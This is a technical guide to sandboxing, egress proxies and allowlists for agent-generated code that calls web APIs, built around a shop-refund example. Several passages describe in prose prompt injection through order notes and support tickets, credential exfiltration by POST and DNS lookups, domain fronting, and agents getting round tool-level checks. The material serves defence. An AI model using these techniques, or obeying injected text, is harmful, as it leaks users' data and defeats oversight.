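# Sandboxing and permission control for LLM-generated code that calls external APIs

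## How an agent's code reaches a web API, and what can go wrong

Sandboxing and permission control limit what a program can do while it runs. They matter most when nobody has read the program first, which is usually true of the many programs that AI agents write. An agent is a language model that software runs in a loop. The model outputs text, and the software carries out any action requested in the text and returns the result to the model as new input. Increasingly, that action is to run a short program the model has just written for the task.

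Many of these programs exist to call an external API. An API (application programming interface) is the set of requests that one piece of software accepts from another, and an external API belongs to another organisation. A program usually calls it over the internet using HTTP, the protocol that also carries web pages. The program gains access by presenting a credential, which is a key, token or password that proves on whose authority it is calling.

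Suppose a shop owner asks an agent to list last month's orders, refund order 1042 and post a summary to the sales channel. This one request takes three API calls. The first is a read call, which only fetches data, in this case the orders from the shop platform. The other two are write calls, which change something on a server. The second call moves money by refunding the customer through the same platform, and the third posts the summary to a chat service.

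### Why agents write programs

In the older method, which *Code Mode* (Varda and Pai) describes, the model makes one tool call at a time. It outputs a marker that isn't a word, then a short structured message naming a tool and its arguments, then a closing marker. The surrounding software stops the model, makes the call and adds the result to the model's input before the model can start the next call. The shop's whole order list therefore passes through the model just so that it can pick out one order and copy its number into the refund.

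A program instead holds the list in a variable, finds the order and sends the refund, and the model sees only what the program prints. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a common standard for connecting agents to outside systems. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* gives an example in which the agent loads only the tool descriptions it needs, which cuts usage from 150,000 tokens (words and pieces of words) to 2,000.

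That figure is an illustration, but measurements also favor code. Rai (2026), in *Beyond Plain MCP*, ran three open-weight models on simulated office software with 42 tools. Writing code used 70 to 90% fewer tokens than ordinary tool calls. It raised the success rate from 86% to 99% for one model and from 36% to 56% for another; the third model's gain was too small to distinguish from chance. Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026), in *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, compared the two methods on 14 models and found code at least as accurate in 11. The other three were older OpenAI models that garbled line breaks, which crashed any script longer than one line. On chains of twelve or more calls, code's advantage reached 18.8 percentage points. *Fewer Tokens, Better Action* (2026) reports 14% higher success and 65% fewer tokens for code when a current model, GPT-6 Astra, controlled robots.

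Patel and colleagues used stand-in tools that recorded their arguments and contacted no service, so their result does not show how well a program handles a real reply. On that question, Rai found that success fell by 22.7 points for one model and 39.5 for another without a description of what each tool returns. An agent that writes the whole program up front has to know the structure of each reply before receiving it.

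Code is also harder to control than tool calls. Software can check a tool call's target against a list before the call runs, but a program can assemble its target while running, from pieces that came from elsewhere. Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues (2026), in *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution*, identified sixteen classes of attack that letting agents act through code introduces or makes worse.

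### What an HTTP request contains

The shop's refund, as it travels over the network, might look like this:

```
POST /refunds HTTP/1.1
Host: api.shop.example
Authorization: Bearer SHOP-KEY
Content-Type: application/json

{"order_id": 450789469, "amount": "38.00"}
```

The host is the server that should receive the request. The method, here POST, specifies the kind of operation. GET retrieves data, POST sends data for the server to act on, and there are a few others, such as DELETE. The path, `/refunds`, identifies a function or a record on that server, and parameters such as a range of dates may follow it after a question mark. The headers come next and hold information about the request, including the credential. "Bearer" means that the server will accept the key from anyone who sends it. The body, after the blank line, holds the data.

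The server replies with a status code and usually a body. Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, got the common codes when testing a system that keeps keys away from agents. GitHub returned 200, meaning success, to a request with a valid credential. OpenAI's API returned 401 to a request without one. FRED, an economic-data service, returned 400, the code for a bad request, because the key was in a header and the service required it among the parameters. A 200 shows only that the server accepted the request, which may still have been the wrong one.

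A request's HTTP method indicates only roughly how dangerous the call is, and sometimes doesn't indicate it at all. In April 2026 an agent deleted a company's production data on the hosting provider Railway. *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that* (Abdelwahab) shows the request, a POST to a general-purpose path with `volumeDelete` in the body. That API uses GraphQL, a query language in which the body names the operation, so a filter that checked only host, method and path would have missed the deletion. The shop's builder may well face the same problem, because new public Shopify apps have had to use GraphQL since April 2025, according to Shopify's *Refund* page.

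### A careless first version

An agent could plausibly write the following program for the owner's request. The builder has put both keys in environment variables and runs the code on an ordinary laptop.

```python
import json, os
from http.client import HTTPSConnection

def call(host, method, path, key, body=None):
    conn = HTTPSConnection(host)
    conn.request(method, path, json.dumps(body) if body else None,
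                 {"Authorization": "Bearer " + key, "Content-Type": "application/json"})
    return json.loads(conn.getresponse().read())

shop_key, chat_key = os.environ["SHOP_KEY"], os.environ["CHAT_KEY"]
orders = call("api.shop.example", "GET", "/orders?from=2026-11-01&to=2026-11-30", shop_key)
order = next(o for o in orders if o["name"].endswith("1042"))
call("api.shop.example", "POST", "/refunds", shop_key,
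     {"order_id": order["id"], "amount": order["total"]})
call("api.chat.example", "POST", "/messages", chat_key,
     {"channel": "sales", "text": f"{len(orders)} orders in November; refunded {order['name']}"})
print(orders)
```

Environment variables are named values that the operating system gives a program when it starts. Developers use them to keep keys out of source code, which works, but any line of the program can read them, and by default so can any program it starts. The code can also reach more than the two keys. Li, Huang and colleagues (2026) point out in *Ring-0 by Default* that a coding agent, by default, runs its model's output with the full authority of the person using the machine.

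The parameters `from` and `to` are guesses. If the shop's API expects `created_min` and `created_max`, a strict server will return a 400 error, but a lenient one will ignore the unknown names and return every order since the shop opened, with a status of 200. The chat message will then report years of orders as November's. Invented parameters were once very common. *Benchmarking Web API Integration Code Generation* (Maninger, Chemnitz and colleagues, 2025) tested models that are now long out of date on writing calls to four real APIs, including Slack's, from memory. For some open models, as many as 39% of the URLs did not exist, and even GPT-4o got only 60% of the calls right when it had to supply the URL itself.

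In *Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations* (2026), Maninger, Chemnitz and colleagues put the relevant documentation into the prompt, which reduced made-up API details but led models to add parameters that the task did not need. They also blocked any text that the API's specification forbids at each step of the model's output, which eliminated illegal addresses, methods and arguments. A legal argument can still hold the wrong value. *SilentProbe* (2026) argues that catching such errors depends on whether the API states its constraints in a form that software can read.

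To issue the refund, the program needs the API's identifier for the order, which differs from the "order 1042" that people use. An order path in Shopify's documentation, for example, contains the number 450789469. The program finds the identifier by taking the first order whose displayed name ends in 1042. A shop that numbers its web and counter sales separately could have both WEB-1042 and POS-1042, and the program would refund whichever is listed first. It also guesses the amount, since the owner may have meant one item out of five. Shopify tells developers to request a calculation first and create the refund from the result, but this code skips the calculation. Because `call` never checks the status code, the program can also report a refund in the chat that the server refused.

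The function `call` will also attach any key to any host. If two variable names are swapped, the shop's key goes to the chat company, where it may stay in a log for years. An attacker would need to add only one line to read every environment variable and post them all to a server of their choice. Both are cases of exfiltration, meaning that data reaches a party who should not have it.

The last line, `print(orders)`, sends the full list of orders back to the model, including the notes that customers typed at checkout. A note can contain a prompt injection, which is text written to make an agent that reads it follow someone else's instructions. For example, a customer might write that AI agents processing the order must also refund their three previous purchases. The model receives the owner's request and the note as one body of text and cannot reliably separate instructions from data, so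 the next program it writes may issue those refunds.

AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World* recounts a similar attack by Aaron Costello of the security firm AppOmni on agents in ServiceNow, a platform for handling support tickets. Costello planted a line in a ticket telling any AI agent to email out data from someone else's ticket. The agent complied, using other agents that could read customer records and send mail. In the shop example, printing only the number of orders would have kept the note away from the model. But error messages are harder to withhold because the model uses them to fix its program, and Felendler and colleagues show that an attacker can write instructions into those as well.

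### Three sources of harm

*How we contain Claude across products*, Anthropic's May 2026 account of its own designs and incidents, sorts the causes of such failures into user misuse, model misbehaviour and external attackers.

Misuse can be malicious, as when a shop assistant refunds a friend, or careless, as when the owner approves a program without understanding it. Misbehaviour means that the model does harm nobody asked for, as in the Railway case. There, Cursor running Claude Opus 4.6 deleted data belonging to PocketOS, which makes software for car rental firms. Computing's *AI coding agent goes rogue, deletes company database in nine seconds* reports a 30-hour outage. According to Abdelwahab, the agent was trying to fix something unrelated when it found a token on the user's machine that gave access to the whole account. Railway later recovered the data. Better models do not eliminate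 this risk. Anthropic observes that they make fewer plain errors but are better at finding ways around a restriction that nobody thought to write down.

Real cases do not always fit one category. TechRadar's *I thought asking an AI agent to book a gym class* describes a man who asked an agent to move him up a waiting list. The agent removed another customer and could not put that person back, which could be blamed on a careless request or a badly behaved model. In a test inside Anthropic, a researcher emailed an employee a harmless-looking prompt to paste into Claude Code, the company's coding agent. The setup steps included an instruction to read a file of cloud credentials and POST its contents to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. The attacker was external, but the instruction came from the user, so defences that look for departures from the user's wishes had nothing to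 detect.

A builder can prevent the damage without settling such questions. A rule that blocks every host except the shop's and the chat service's stops that POST whether the cause is a thief, a confused model or a hurried employee, because the rule checks only the request. Similarly, code cannot send a key anywhere if the key never enters the place where the code runs. Training and instructions, by contrast, change only how likely a model is to do something. On one benchmark of prompt injection, Anthropic reports that attackers' success rate against Claude Opus 4.7 is about 0.1% on a single attempt, but 5 to 6% after a hundred attempts that adapt to its defences.

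However, a limit on one tool may not stop an agent from doing the same thing another way. Li and colleagues found coding agents that refused to write a file through their file tool and then wrote it through the command line, because the check applied only to the file tool, not to the whole process. Limits also don't prevent harm from calls they allow. The wrong refund goes to a permitted host, with a valid key, in the correct format. Kenney and colleagues note that in their own system, an agent that holds no secret can still make a destructive call within its authority. So the shop needs several limits, each on a different property of the call.

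### Where each control acts

Felendler and colleagues divide the process into four phases: finding the tools, writing the code, running it, and returning the result. If something fails, the process goes back to writing the code. The diagram shows the shop's program going through these phases and then into storage. The controls on the right all act outside the model.

```
Owner sends the request
        |
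Agent reads the API's documentation and writes a program
        |
Program runs            <-- SANDBOX: limits files, processes and network access
        |
Request leaves          <-- EGRESS PROXY: refuses hosts that are not on the allowlist
        |
Rules apply             <-- PERMISSION RULES: allow the call, refuse it or ask a person
        |
Owner confirms          <-- CONFIRMATION: only for calls that the rules send to a person
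        |
Request gets its key    <-- CREDENTIAL BROKER: adds the key outside the sandbox
        |
External API replies
        |
Reply comes back        <-- RESPONSE CHECKS: look for errors and for missing data
        |                   REDACTION: removes credentials from output and logs
Agent reads the output  --> after a failure, back to writing the program
        |
Program goes to storage <-- ADMISSION CHECK: before the program enters the store
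        |
Program runs again      <-- REUSE CHECK: each time, along with every control above
```

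## Choosing the boundary around the running code

On an ordinary laptop, the shop's program can read every file its owner can read and connect to any server. It does both through the kernel, the core of the operating system, which controls the disk, network and other hardware. To open a file, a program makes a system call, and the kernel either opens the file or returns an error. Sandboxes differ mainly in what they place between the program and the kernel of the host, the machine the builder wants to protect.

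### How each kind of boundary works

The lightest sandboxes run the program directly on the host's kernel, which blocks more system calls than usual. On macOS, a built-in framework called Seatbelt checks the program's file and network operations against a policy. On Linux, a tool called bubblewrap makes only chosen folders visible to the program and can remove its network access. Seccomp, a Linux kernel feature, blocks whole types of system call. Any process the program starts inherits the same limits.

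Such limits close the gap that Li and colleagues found between an agent's file tool and its command line, but only if everything the agent uses runs inside them. Anthropic explains that Claude Code's built-in sandbox covers shell commands. Claude Code's file tools and any MCP servers run directly on the host unless the user puts the whole agent inside a boundary.

A container gives a program its own packaged files and libraries, and a separate view of the machine's processes and network. The program still makes system calls to the host's kernel, and *Tracekit Box* (2026) points out that one kernel bug therefore exposes every container on the machine. gVisor reduces that exposure with a second kernel, which runs as an ordinary program between the container and the host and handles most system calls itself. Anthropic uses gVisor for code that Claude runs in the claude.ai chat product. The extra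 layer slows programs down, and *Sandlock* (2026) notes compatibility problems with build tools that depend on fine details of system calls.

A virtual machine has its own kernel, which runs on hardware simulated by a program on the host called the virtual machine monitor. Malicious code that takes over this kernel still has to break out through the monitor. Firecracker, a monitor built for short cloud jobs, simulates only a few devices, which leaves little to attack. According to *SideKernel* (2026), its users include Amazon, for the Lambda service, and E2B and Vercel, which rent out sandboxes for agents. The machines still share a processor, however. *AI Code Sandboxes* (2026) cites a 2023 experiment in which Weissman and colleagues leaked data between Firecracker machines through the processor. The same method failed when they tried it without virtual machines.

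V8 is the engine that runs JavaScript in the Chrome browser, and an isolate is one instance of it with its own memory. JavaScript has no instruction for making a system call, so code in an isolate can reach anything outside it only through functions that the surrounding program provides. WebAssembly, a compact instruction format to which other languages can compile, has the same restriction. *External sandboxes for coding agents* (Willison, 2026) describes a prototype in which a simulated PC, compiled to WebAssembly, boots Linux inside an ordinary Node.js process. The agent's commands run in that Linux system and can access only the folders the user shares.

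An interpreter, the program that reads and runs code, can also be the boundary if it lacks the dangerous operations. Monty is a small Python interpreter from the software company Pydantic. According to the podcast Talk Python, code running in Monty has no access to files, environment variables or the network unless the application that embeds Monty grants it.

### What the boundaries cost

Many of the published timings come from companies that make one of the options. In *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster*, Varda, Pai and Gupta of Cloudflare compare two that the company sells. They report that containers take hundreds of milliseconds to start and use hundreds of megabytes of memory, while isolates take a few milliseconds and use a few megabytes. Pydantic, which makes Monty, timed the alternatives to it. A Docker container took 195 ms, and standard Python compiled to WebAssembly took 16 ms.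 Pyodide, another WebAssembly build of Python, took 2.7 seconds inside the JavaScript runtime Deno.

| Boundary | What an escape requires | Start-up | Memory | Languages | Figures from |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Process restrictions | A bug in the host's kernel or a gap in the policy | Under 10 ms (a design goal) | Little beyond the program's own | Any installed on the host | *Sandlock* |
| Container | A bug in the host's kernel or a gap in the set-up | 195 ms; "hundreds" | Hundreds of MB | Any | Pydantic; Varda and colleagues |
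| Container with gVisor | A bug in gVisor's kernel, then one in the host's | A container's, then slower system calls | A container's plus gVisor's | Any, with some incompatible tools | *Tracekit Box* |
| Virtual machine (Firecracker) | A bug in the monitor or the processor | Low hundreds of ms | The program's plus a second kernel's | Any | *Tracekit Box* |
| V8 isolate | A bug in V8, then one in any outer layer | A few ms | A few MB | JavaScript; Python and WebAssembly load more slowly | Varda and colleagues |
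| WebAssembly | A bug in the WebAssembly runtime | 16 ms to 2.7 s for Python | Depends on what runs inside | Any that compile to it | Pydantic |
| Small interpreter (Monty) | A bug in the interpreter or in a function it exposes | About 6 microseconds | A share of the host program's | A subset of Python | Talk Python |

The rows are not ranked by security. *SideKernel* treats containers as weaker than small virtual machines but leaves open how Seatbelt compares, because under Seatbelt the host's kernel is exposed but also enforces a policy.

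Start-up times for an empty sandbox also leave out work that a real program needs. *Readie* (2026) attributes long start-up times to fetching and loading libraries and data, and shortens them by restoring a sandbox from a memory snapshot with the libraries already loaded. The shop's program uses only Python's standard library, so it has little of this delay.

To imitate an agent that issues ten commands in a row, Pydantic's test had the sandboxes without a lasting session run the first command, then the first and second, and so on up to all ten. Rerunning arithmetic is harmless, but if the shop's second command issued a refund, the customer would get nine refunds. A builder who chooses a sandbox without a lasting session has to save results between commands or put all the calls into one program.

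### Codex, Cowork and Dynamic Workers

OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, restricts processes on the user's own machine, using Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap and seccomp on Linux. OpenAI's *Inside the Codex sandbox* explains why the company did not use containers or virtual machines. Many developers have customized their laptops over years, and copying that setup into a container takes work. Some tools also run only on the host.

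The default profile lets commands write inside the workspace, the project's folder. Two subfolders, `.git` and `.codex`, stay read-only because a change there could make other software run the agent's code later or alter Codex's own settings. Commands can read almost anything the user can, because compilers and other tools depend on files scattered around the machine. They have no network access. The profile therefore protects the user's other files from changes but leaves secrets readable, including API keys in configuration files.

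Letting the program read files is tolerable only while the network is off, since a program that reads a key cannot send it anywhere. The shop's program needs the network for its first call. A builder who allows network access should also restrict which files the program can read, and OpenAI's *Permissions* shows how to deny access to particular folders or to all files with a given extension.

Sandboxed code can also escape later by changing a file that a program outside the sandbox will run. OpenAI gives the example of an agent that alters the copy of Prettier, a code formatter, in the project's folder. If the user's editor runs Prettier each time a file is saved, the altered copy will run outside the sandbox with the user's full permissions.

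The first version of OpenAI's Codex sandbox for Windows appeared to block the network, but programs could get around the block. According to Wiesen's *Building a safe, effective sandbox to enable Codex on Windows*, it set environment variables that sent web traffic to a dead address. Programs that read those variables failed to connect, but a program could ignore them and open a connection directly. The shop's careless program would have done so by accident, because Python's `HTTPSConnection` does not read proxy variables. The current version runs commands under a separate Windows user account, and the Windows firewall blocks all outgoing traffic from that account. Setting this up requires administrator rights, which the team had hoped to avoid.

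Most users of Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work, can't judge a shell command, so Anthropic wanted a boundary that never depends on their approval. Cowork runs generated code in a virtual machine on the user's computer, with its own Linux kernel, file system and list of processes. On the host, the code can access only the folder the user selected and Cowork's settings folder. The user can share a folder as read-only, as writable, or as writable without permission to delete. Unlike the Codex default, this design prevents the code from reading a credentials file elsewhere on the disk, but it can't protect the shared folder itself from a harmful program.

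Cowork at first ran the agent's loop inside the virtual machine along with the code, so it was unusable whenever the machine failed to start. Anthropic moved the loop outside and kept the code inside, so that Claude can still respond and help fix the problem. Willison chose the same arrangement because an agent outside the sandbox can't modify itself or its surroundings, and because the boundary is easier to audit. Anthropic also moved local MCP servers onto the host, where the virtual machine no longer restricts them.

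The design also makes monitoring harder for companies, because security software on an employee's computer registers the virtual machine as a single process and can't inspect the activity inside it. Administrators can export event logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this is not the same as live monitoring.

With Cloudflare's Dynamic Workers, an application passes the generated code to Cloudflare's platform, which starts a new isolate for it, usually on the same machine and even in the same thread as the application. The isolate can run one program and then be discarded. Varda and colleagues argue that because containers start slowly, builders are tempted to reuse one for several tasks, which lets one task's data or damage reach the next. Isolates start quickly, so builders have little reason to reuse them.

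With V8 isolates, the application decides what the code can reach. It can hand over specific functions, such as one that posts to a chat room, and a single setting cuts off the internet. But the builder gives up the shell, ordinary installed programs and, in practice, most languages other than JavaScript. Varda and colleagues say that security bugs are more common in V8 than in the software that runs virtual machines. To compensate, Cloudflare puts a second sandbox around the first, scans for malicious code and installs V8 patches within hours. A builder who runs isolates on a private server doesn't get these protections automatically.

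### Executing only permitted statements

The other boundaries let a program attempt anything and block some of the results. *STELP* (Shinde, Wadhwa and colleagues, 2026) describes a system from the bank Capital One that examines the program itself. The system parses the Python code into a syntax tree, in which each assignment, loop or function call is a node, and compares the tree with a configuration that lists the permitted statement types, packages and functions. The shop's careless program begins with `import json, os`. If the configuration permitted `json` but not `os`, which exposes environment variables, the system would reject the program at that line.

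If the tree passes, STELP walks through it and executes one node at a time, keeping track of the variables, instead of handing the whole program to Python. For `x = 1 + 3`, it evaluates the two numbers, adds them and stores the result. When it reaches a call to an outside tool, it checks that the configuration allows the tool and applies a time limit.

Some violations appear only during this second stage. In one of the paper's examples, a program searches Wikipedia, writes to a database and then tries to open a network connection. STELP stops it at that last line, after the earlier calls have already taken effect. A shop program stopped in the same way could issue a refund without sending the chat message.

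Shinde and colleagues tested STELP on 164 safe programs and 470 versions into which a language model had inserted flaws such as infinite loops or the execution of downloaded code. STELP blocked all the unsafe programs and ran 98.1% of the safe ones. CodeShield, Meta's scanner for known bad patterns, blocked 68% of the unsafe programs and allowed 93% of the safe ones. On 361 other programs, STELP's output always matched the expected output. STELP added a median of 0.19 ms to the running time, and at most 520 ms.

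When STELP rejected a program, a second model generated an explanation of the problem for the model that had written the code. With this explanation, the first model repaired 90.2% of the samples within two attempts, while 8% needed more than ten.

STELP's perfect blocking score is limited evidence of its security. The team configured STELP with the fewest permissions that the benchmark's safe programs needed, then adjusted the configuration slightly. Most of the unsafe programs failed because they used a function or package outside that list, which any strict list would catch. Nobody in the test tried to defeat STELP specifically. The team also chose the 361 programs for compatibility with its configuration, so the matching outputs don't show how often ordinary generated code would fall outside the permitted subset.

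An attacker who found a gap in STELP's checks would have all the authority of a normal Python process. Shinde and colleagues recommend combining STELP with other layers. Inside a container or virtual machine, STELP would give the agent an early, specific explanation of what it may not do, and the outer boundary would still confine the code if STELP's check failed.

### When the sandbox does not start

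A program can also run without its sandbox. GitLab, a platform for storing and building software, runs its agents' jobs inside Anthropic's Sandbox Runtime, a package based on Seatbelt and bubblewrap. On Linux, the package has to create namespaces, which give a process its own view of users and files. If the job lacks the privilege to create them, it prints a warning in its log and runs the agent without the sandbox, according to GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox*. The list of permitted domains then no longer applies, and the agent can contact any server that the machine can. GitLab's guide to checking the rules warns that an unprotected flow can still run normally.

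This can happen on an ordinary machine. According to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, Ubuntu 24.04 and later by default stop bubblewrap from creating the namespaces it needs. Much like GitLab, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without a sandbox if the sandbox can't start, unless the user has turned on `failIfUnavailable`. Codex on macOS is safer because it refuses to run a command if Seatbelt can't enforce the chosen policy.

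GitLab 19.6 added a setting, "Don't run flows when the sandbox is unavailable", which makes the job fail instead. However, GitLab checks only that a command named `srt` exists, so a project that supplies its own container image or set-up script controls what that command does. The set-up script is also a risk because it runs before the sandbox starts and can read variables that, according to GitLab, include access tokens of the person who triggered the job.

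For the shop, the builder can have the launcher test the boundary before each run. From inside the sandbox, the launcher tries to read a forbidden file and contact a forbidden server, and it stops if either attempt succeeds. This test would also catch a missing settings file. Anthropic's runtime starts even when its default settings file is missing, with the network off and writes confined, but without the builder's rules about which files to hide.

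### A boundary for the shop

The shop's program makes three API calls and sorts some data between them. It needs no shell, installed tools or files. A sandbox like Codex's would leave it on a machine full of software and files it never uses. A virtual machine would separate it from the host more strongly, but would also give it a complete operating system that an attacker could exploit through an injected instruction. Cloudflare's *Agents have their own computers with Sandboxes GA* recommends a full computer for agents that work like developers, copying repositories and building software, and something lighter for other agents.

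A hosted isolate suits this job best. Code in it starts with no files to read and no programs to launch, so the builder adds the few things it needs instead of having to find and remove everything else. Its speed is only a minor advantage, because a model usually takes seconds to write the program and the owner won't notice another 200 ms. The price is also low. Cloudflare set it at $0.002 a day for each different program, plus processing time, and waived the charge during the test period. Twenty new programs a day would cost four cents before processing time.

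Monty would start even faster, and Pydantic argues that many agents don't need a full sandbox. But the open-source version runs on the same machine as the application that calls it, so code that escaped would land on the machine where the shop's agent software keeps its other data. Code that escaped a hosted isolate would land on Cloudflare's machines, which are protected by the second layer and the company's security team. The shop's builder probably couldn't match either. Anthropic's experience also supports using established parts. Its hypervisor (the software that runs virtual machines), gVisor and seccomp have been dependable, while a component the company wrote itself failed.

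The agent must now write JavaScript, which current models do well. If a later task needs a Python library that won't run in an isolate, the builder can use a Firecracker machine or a gVisor container with no folders shared from the host. Either way, each program should get a fresh sandbox, so one month's orders aren't still in memory when the next program runs.

The builder's code for starting the isolate is short:

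```js
const task = env.LOADER.load({
  compatibilityDate: "2026-03-01",
  mainModule: "task.js",
  modules: { "task.js": generatedCode },
  env: {},               // no keys, and no functions from outside
  globalOutbound: null   // no network
});
```

With these settings, the program can't read the owner's files or either key. It also can't list the orders, because it has no route to the shop's server.

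## Restricting which servers the code can reach

The shop's program needs to reach two servers, one for the orders and the refund and one for the chat message. Ordinary internet access would also let it reach any other server on the internet. A program with that much access can do harm without breaking out of its sandbox. *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox* (Tuttle, 2026) points out that the program can send whatever it can read to someone else's machine.

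The usual method is an egress proxy, a program outside the sandbox that all outgoing traffic must pass through. The proxy lets the code contact only the servers on an allowlist.

### How the traffic reaches the proxy

A proxy is useful only if the code has no other way out. The builder therefore removes the sandbox's own network access and adds back a single connection. On Linux, a request to the shop's server would travel like this:

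1. The launcher starts the program in a network namespace (a private view of the network) that has no link to the real one. Direct connections to outside servers fail.
2. The launcher gives the program a Unix socket, which is a channel between two processes on the same machine. The proxy listens at the other end, outside the sandbox.
3. The program asks the proxy for a connection to `api.shop.example` on port 443, the standard port for HTTPS. It sends the name, without looking up the numerical address.
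4. The proxy looks for the name on the allowlist. If the name is missing, the proxy returns a 403 error and contacts nobody.
5. If the name is there, the proxy looks up its IP address and checks that this isn't an internal address.
6. The proxy connects to the address it has just checked and passes data in both directions.

Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes a socket and an outside proxy of this kind for Claude Code. Other boundaries change only the first two steps. On macOS, Seatbelt blocks every connection except the one to the proxy. For containers, Anthropic suggests Docker's `--network none` option, with the proxy's socket mounted as a file. A Firecracker virtual machine can run without an outside network interface and instead use vsock, a channel between the virtual machine and its host. In a cloud, firewall rules can block every destination except the proxy.

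A program can ignore proxy variables such as `HTTPS_PROXY`, as happened with the first Codex sandbox for Windows. If the sandbox has no other route, the program fails to connect. Anthropic says this happens in Claude Code with plain `ssh` and most database drivers, even when the server is on the allowlist. Vercel's firewall avoids the problem by redirecting every outgoing TCP connection and name lookup to itself, so programs need no proxy settings.

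The shop's isolate makes this even simpler. In the launcher, the builder can replace `globalOutbound: null` with a gateway, a short piece of their own code that runs outside the isolate. Cloudflare then passes every web request from the isolate to the gateway, which acts as the egress proxy.

### Redirects, name lookups and internal addresses

A server can answer a request with a redirect, a reply that names another address to try. An attacker who found a page on the shop's server that redirects to any address could use it to send the program to `files.attacker.example`. To follow the redirect, the program would have to open a new connection, which would fail because Claude Code's proxy checks the host name of every connection. A proxy that follows redirects itself can miss this check, so it should return the redirect to the program instead.

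Code can leak data through a name lookup even if it never connects to the named server. DNS, the system that turns names into addresses, forwards a lookup of `abc.attacker.example` to a server chosen by the owner of `attacker.example`. A program can put stolen data in the first part of the name and receive instructions in the reply. BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter's 'Sandbox' mode allows DNS queries* (2026) describes this weakness in an Amazon service that runs agents' code, in a mode Amazon had advertised as "complete isolation with no external access". BeyondTrust reported the problem in September 2025, and in December Amazon decided to change the documentation instead of the product. Amazon closed the gap in April 2026, a month after BeyondTrust published the finding.

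In the six steps above, the proxy looks up only names on the list, so the code can't use DNS to reach an attacker. Some hosted sandboxes allow this by default. When an allowlist contains a domain, E2B also permits all traffic to 8.8.8.8, Google's public DNS server, even if that address is on the deny list. To block it, the builder has to set an empty list of DNS servers and write the permitted names into the sandbox's hosts file. Vercel filters lookups by the domain list, but if a policy allows only address ranges, the code can look up any name.

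Step 5 must check the address because whoever controls a name chooses its address. If someone pointed a listed name at 127.0.0.1, the address a machine uses for itself, the proxy would connect the code to a program on the proxy's own host. Since version 2.1.284, Anthropic's proxy has refused names that resolve only to local addresses like this one. Earlier versions connected to whatever address came back. The proxy still permits private ranges such as 10.0.0.0/8, because a company may want to list a server on its internal network. The shop's two services are public, so its builder can refuse private ranges too.

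The address 169.254.169.254 is particularly dangerous because on many clouds it belongs to the metadata service, which gives programs on a machine temporary credentials for the cloud account. Trend Micro's *Require MMDSv2 for AgentCore Runtime* recommends a version of the service that requires callers to first obtain a session token with a PUT request. Unit 42, Palo Alto Networks' research group, found that AgentCore's Runtime did not enforce these tokens. Tokens help against an attacker who can only make a program fetch a chosen address, but generated code can send the PUT request itself, so a builder who runs it should block the address altogether.

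### What the proxy can read

HTTPS encrypts requests with a protocol called TLS. Before the encryption starts, the program normally sends the server's name unencrypted, in a field called SNI, so that the server can present the right certificate. A proxy that doesn't decrypt the traffic can read this name, the server's address and the amount of data transferred, but it can't distinguish a request that lists orders from one that issues a refund.

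A firewall that checks only the SNI field can't confirm that the name there is the real destination. In domain fronting, a program puts a permitted name in the SNI field and a different one in the Host header, inside the encrypted request. If one provider's servers host both sites, they may deliver the request to the site in the header. Vercel's *Sandbox firewall* notes that many providers reject mismatched names, but that the firewall does not prevent the mismatch by default. Claude Code's proxy has the same limit. Docker warns that allowing a broad domain such as github.com also permits access to material that any user has put there, so an agent could use the domain to send data out without domain fronting.

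A proxy has to decrypt a request to judge more than the server's name. It presents its own certificate to the program in place of the shop's, decrypts the request, examines it and encrypts it again for the real server. The method and path show whether the request is to list orders or refund one. The headers show whose credential the program is using, and the body shows which order and what amount. Anthropic's hosted version of Claude Code uses this kind of proxy for git, the tool developers use to share code. Before the proxy attaches the GitHub credential, it checks, for example, that the agent is pushing only to the branch the user configured.

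A proxy can decrypt traffic only if the program accepts the proxy's certificate. E2B adds its certificate authority to the sandbox system's list of trusted authorities, but Python's Requests library and Node.js use their own lists and may reject the proxy's certificate until the builder configures them. A program that accepts only one particular certificate will fail. E2B's authority can also change when a paused sandbox resumes on another machine, which breaks programs that loaded the old one at startup.

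Decrypting traffic at the proxy also creates a security risk, because anyone who breaks into the proxy can read the customer data and keys it handles. Vercel reduces this risk by decrypting only the traffic to domains whose rules require it. It also creates a separate certificate authority for each sandbox and discards it when the sandbox stops.

The shop's builder avoids the certificate problems because when code in the isolate calls `fetch`, the platform hands the request to the gateway before encrypting it. The gateway can then read the method, path, headers and body, so it still has to be trustworthy enough to handle customers' data.

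### An allowlist for the shop

The simplest allowlist has two lines:

```
api.shop.example
api.chat.example
```

It would stop an attacker's added line from posting every environment variable to an outside server. However, it permits every function of both services, including many the task never uses. The gateway can narrow the list to the three calls in the owner's request:

```js
const ALLOWED = [
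  "GET https://api.shop.example/orders",
  "POST https://api.shop.example/refunds",
  "POST https://api.chat.example/messages"
];

export class Gateway extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  async fetch(request) {
    const url = new URL(request.url);
    const target = url.origin + url.pathname;
    if (!ALLOWED.includes(request.method + " " + target))
      return new Response("Not on the allowlist", { status: 403 });
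    return fetch(request, { redirect: "manual" });
  }
}
```

The code compares the whole string, so it rejects lookalikes such as `api.shop.example.attacker.net`, unencrypted requests and unusual ports. Looser comparisons are risky. Tuttle's list of recent sandbox escapes includes host names that the policy check and the proxy interpreted differently. The `redirect` setting returns any redirect to the isolate, which must send another request through the gateway to follow it.

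The table compares the two lists, assuming that the program has a working key for each call.

| What the program attempts | Two host names | Host, method and path |
|---|---|---|
| Send the orders to an unlisted server | Refused | Refused |
| Delete a product | Permitted | Refused |
| Tell the shop platform to send all new orders to an outside address | Permitted | Refused |
| Upload a file to the chat service | Permitted | Refused |
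| Refund the wrong order, or refund order 1042 twice | Permitted | Permitted |
| Post customers' addresses in the sales channel | Permitted | Permitted |
| Post the orders to an attacker's account on the chat service | Permitted | Permitted |

The third row matters because many platforms can notify an outside address whenever something happens. If the list contains only host names, the code could register an attacker's address for those notifications. The platform would then send the orders directly to the attacker, bypassing the proxy.

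If the shop's API used GraphQL, as Railway's does, a gateway rule that allowed the refund would also allow deleting a product, so the gateway would need rules based on the contents of the request body.

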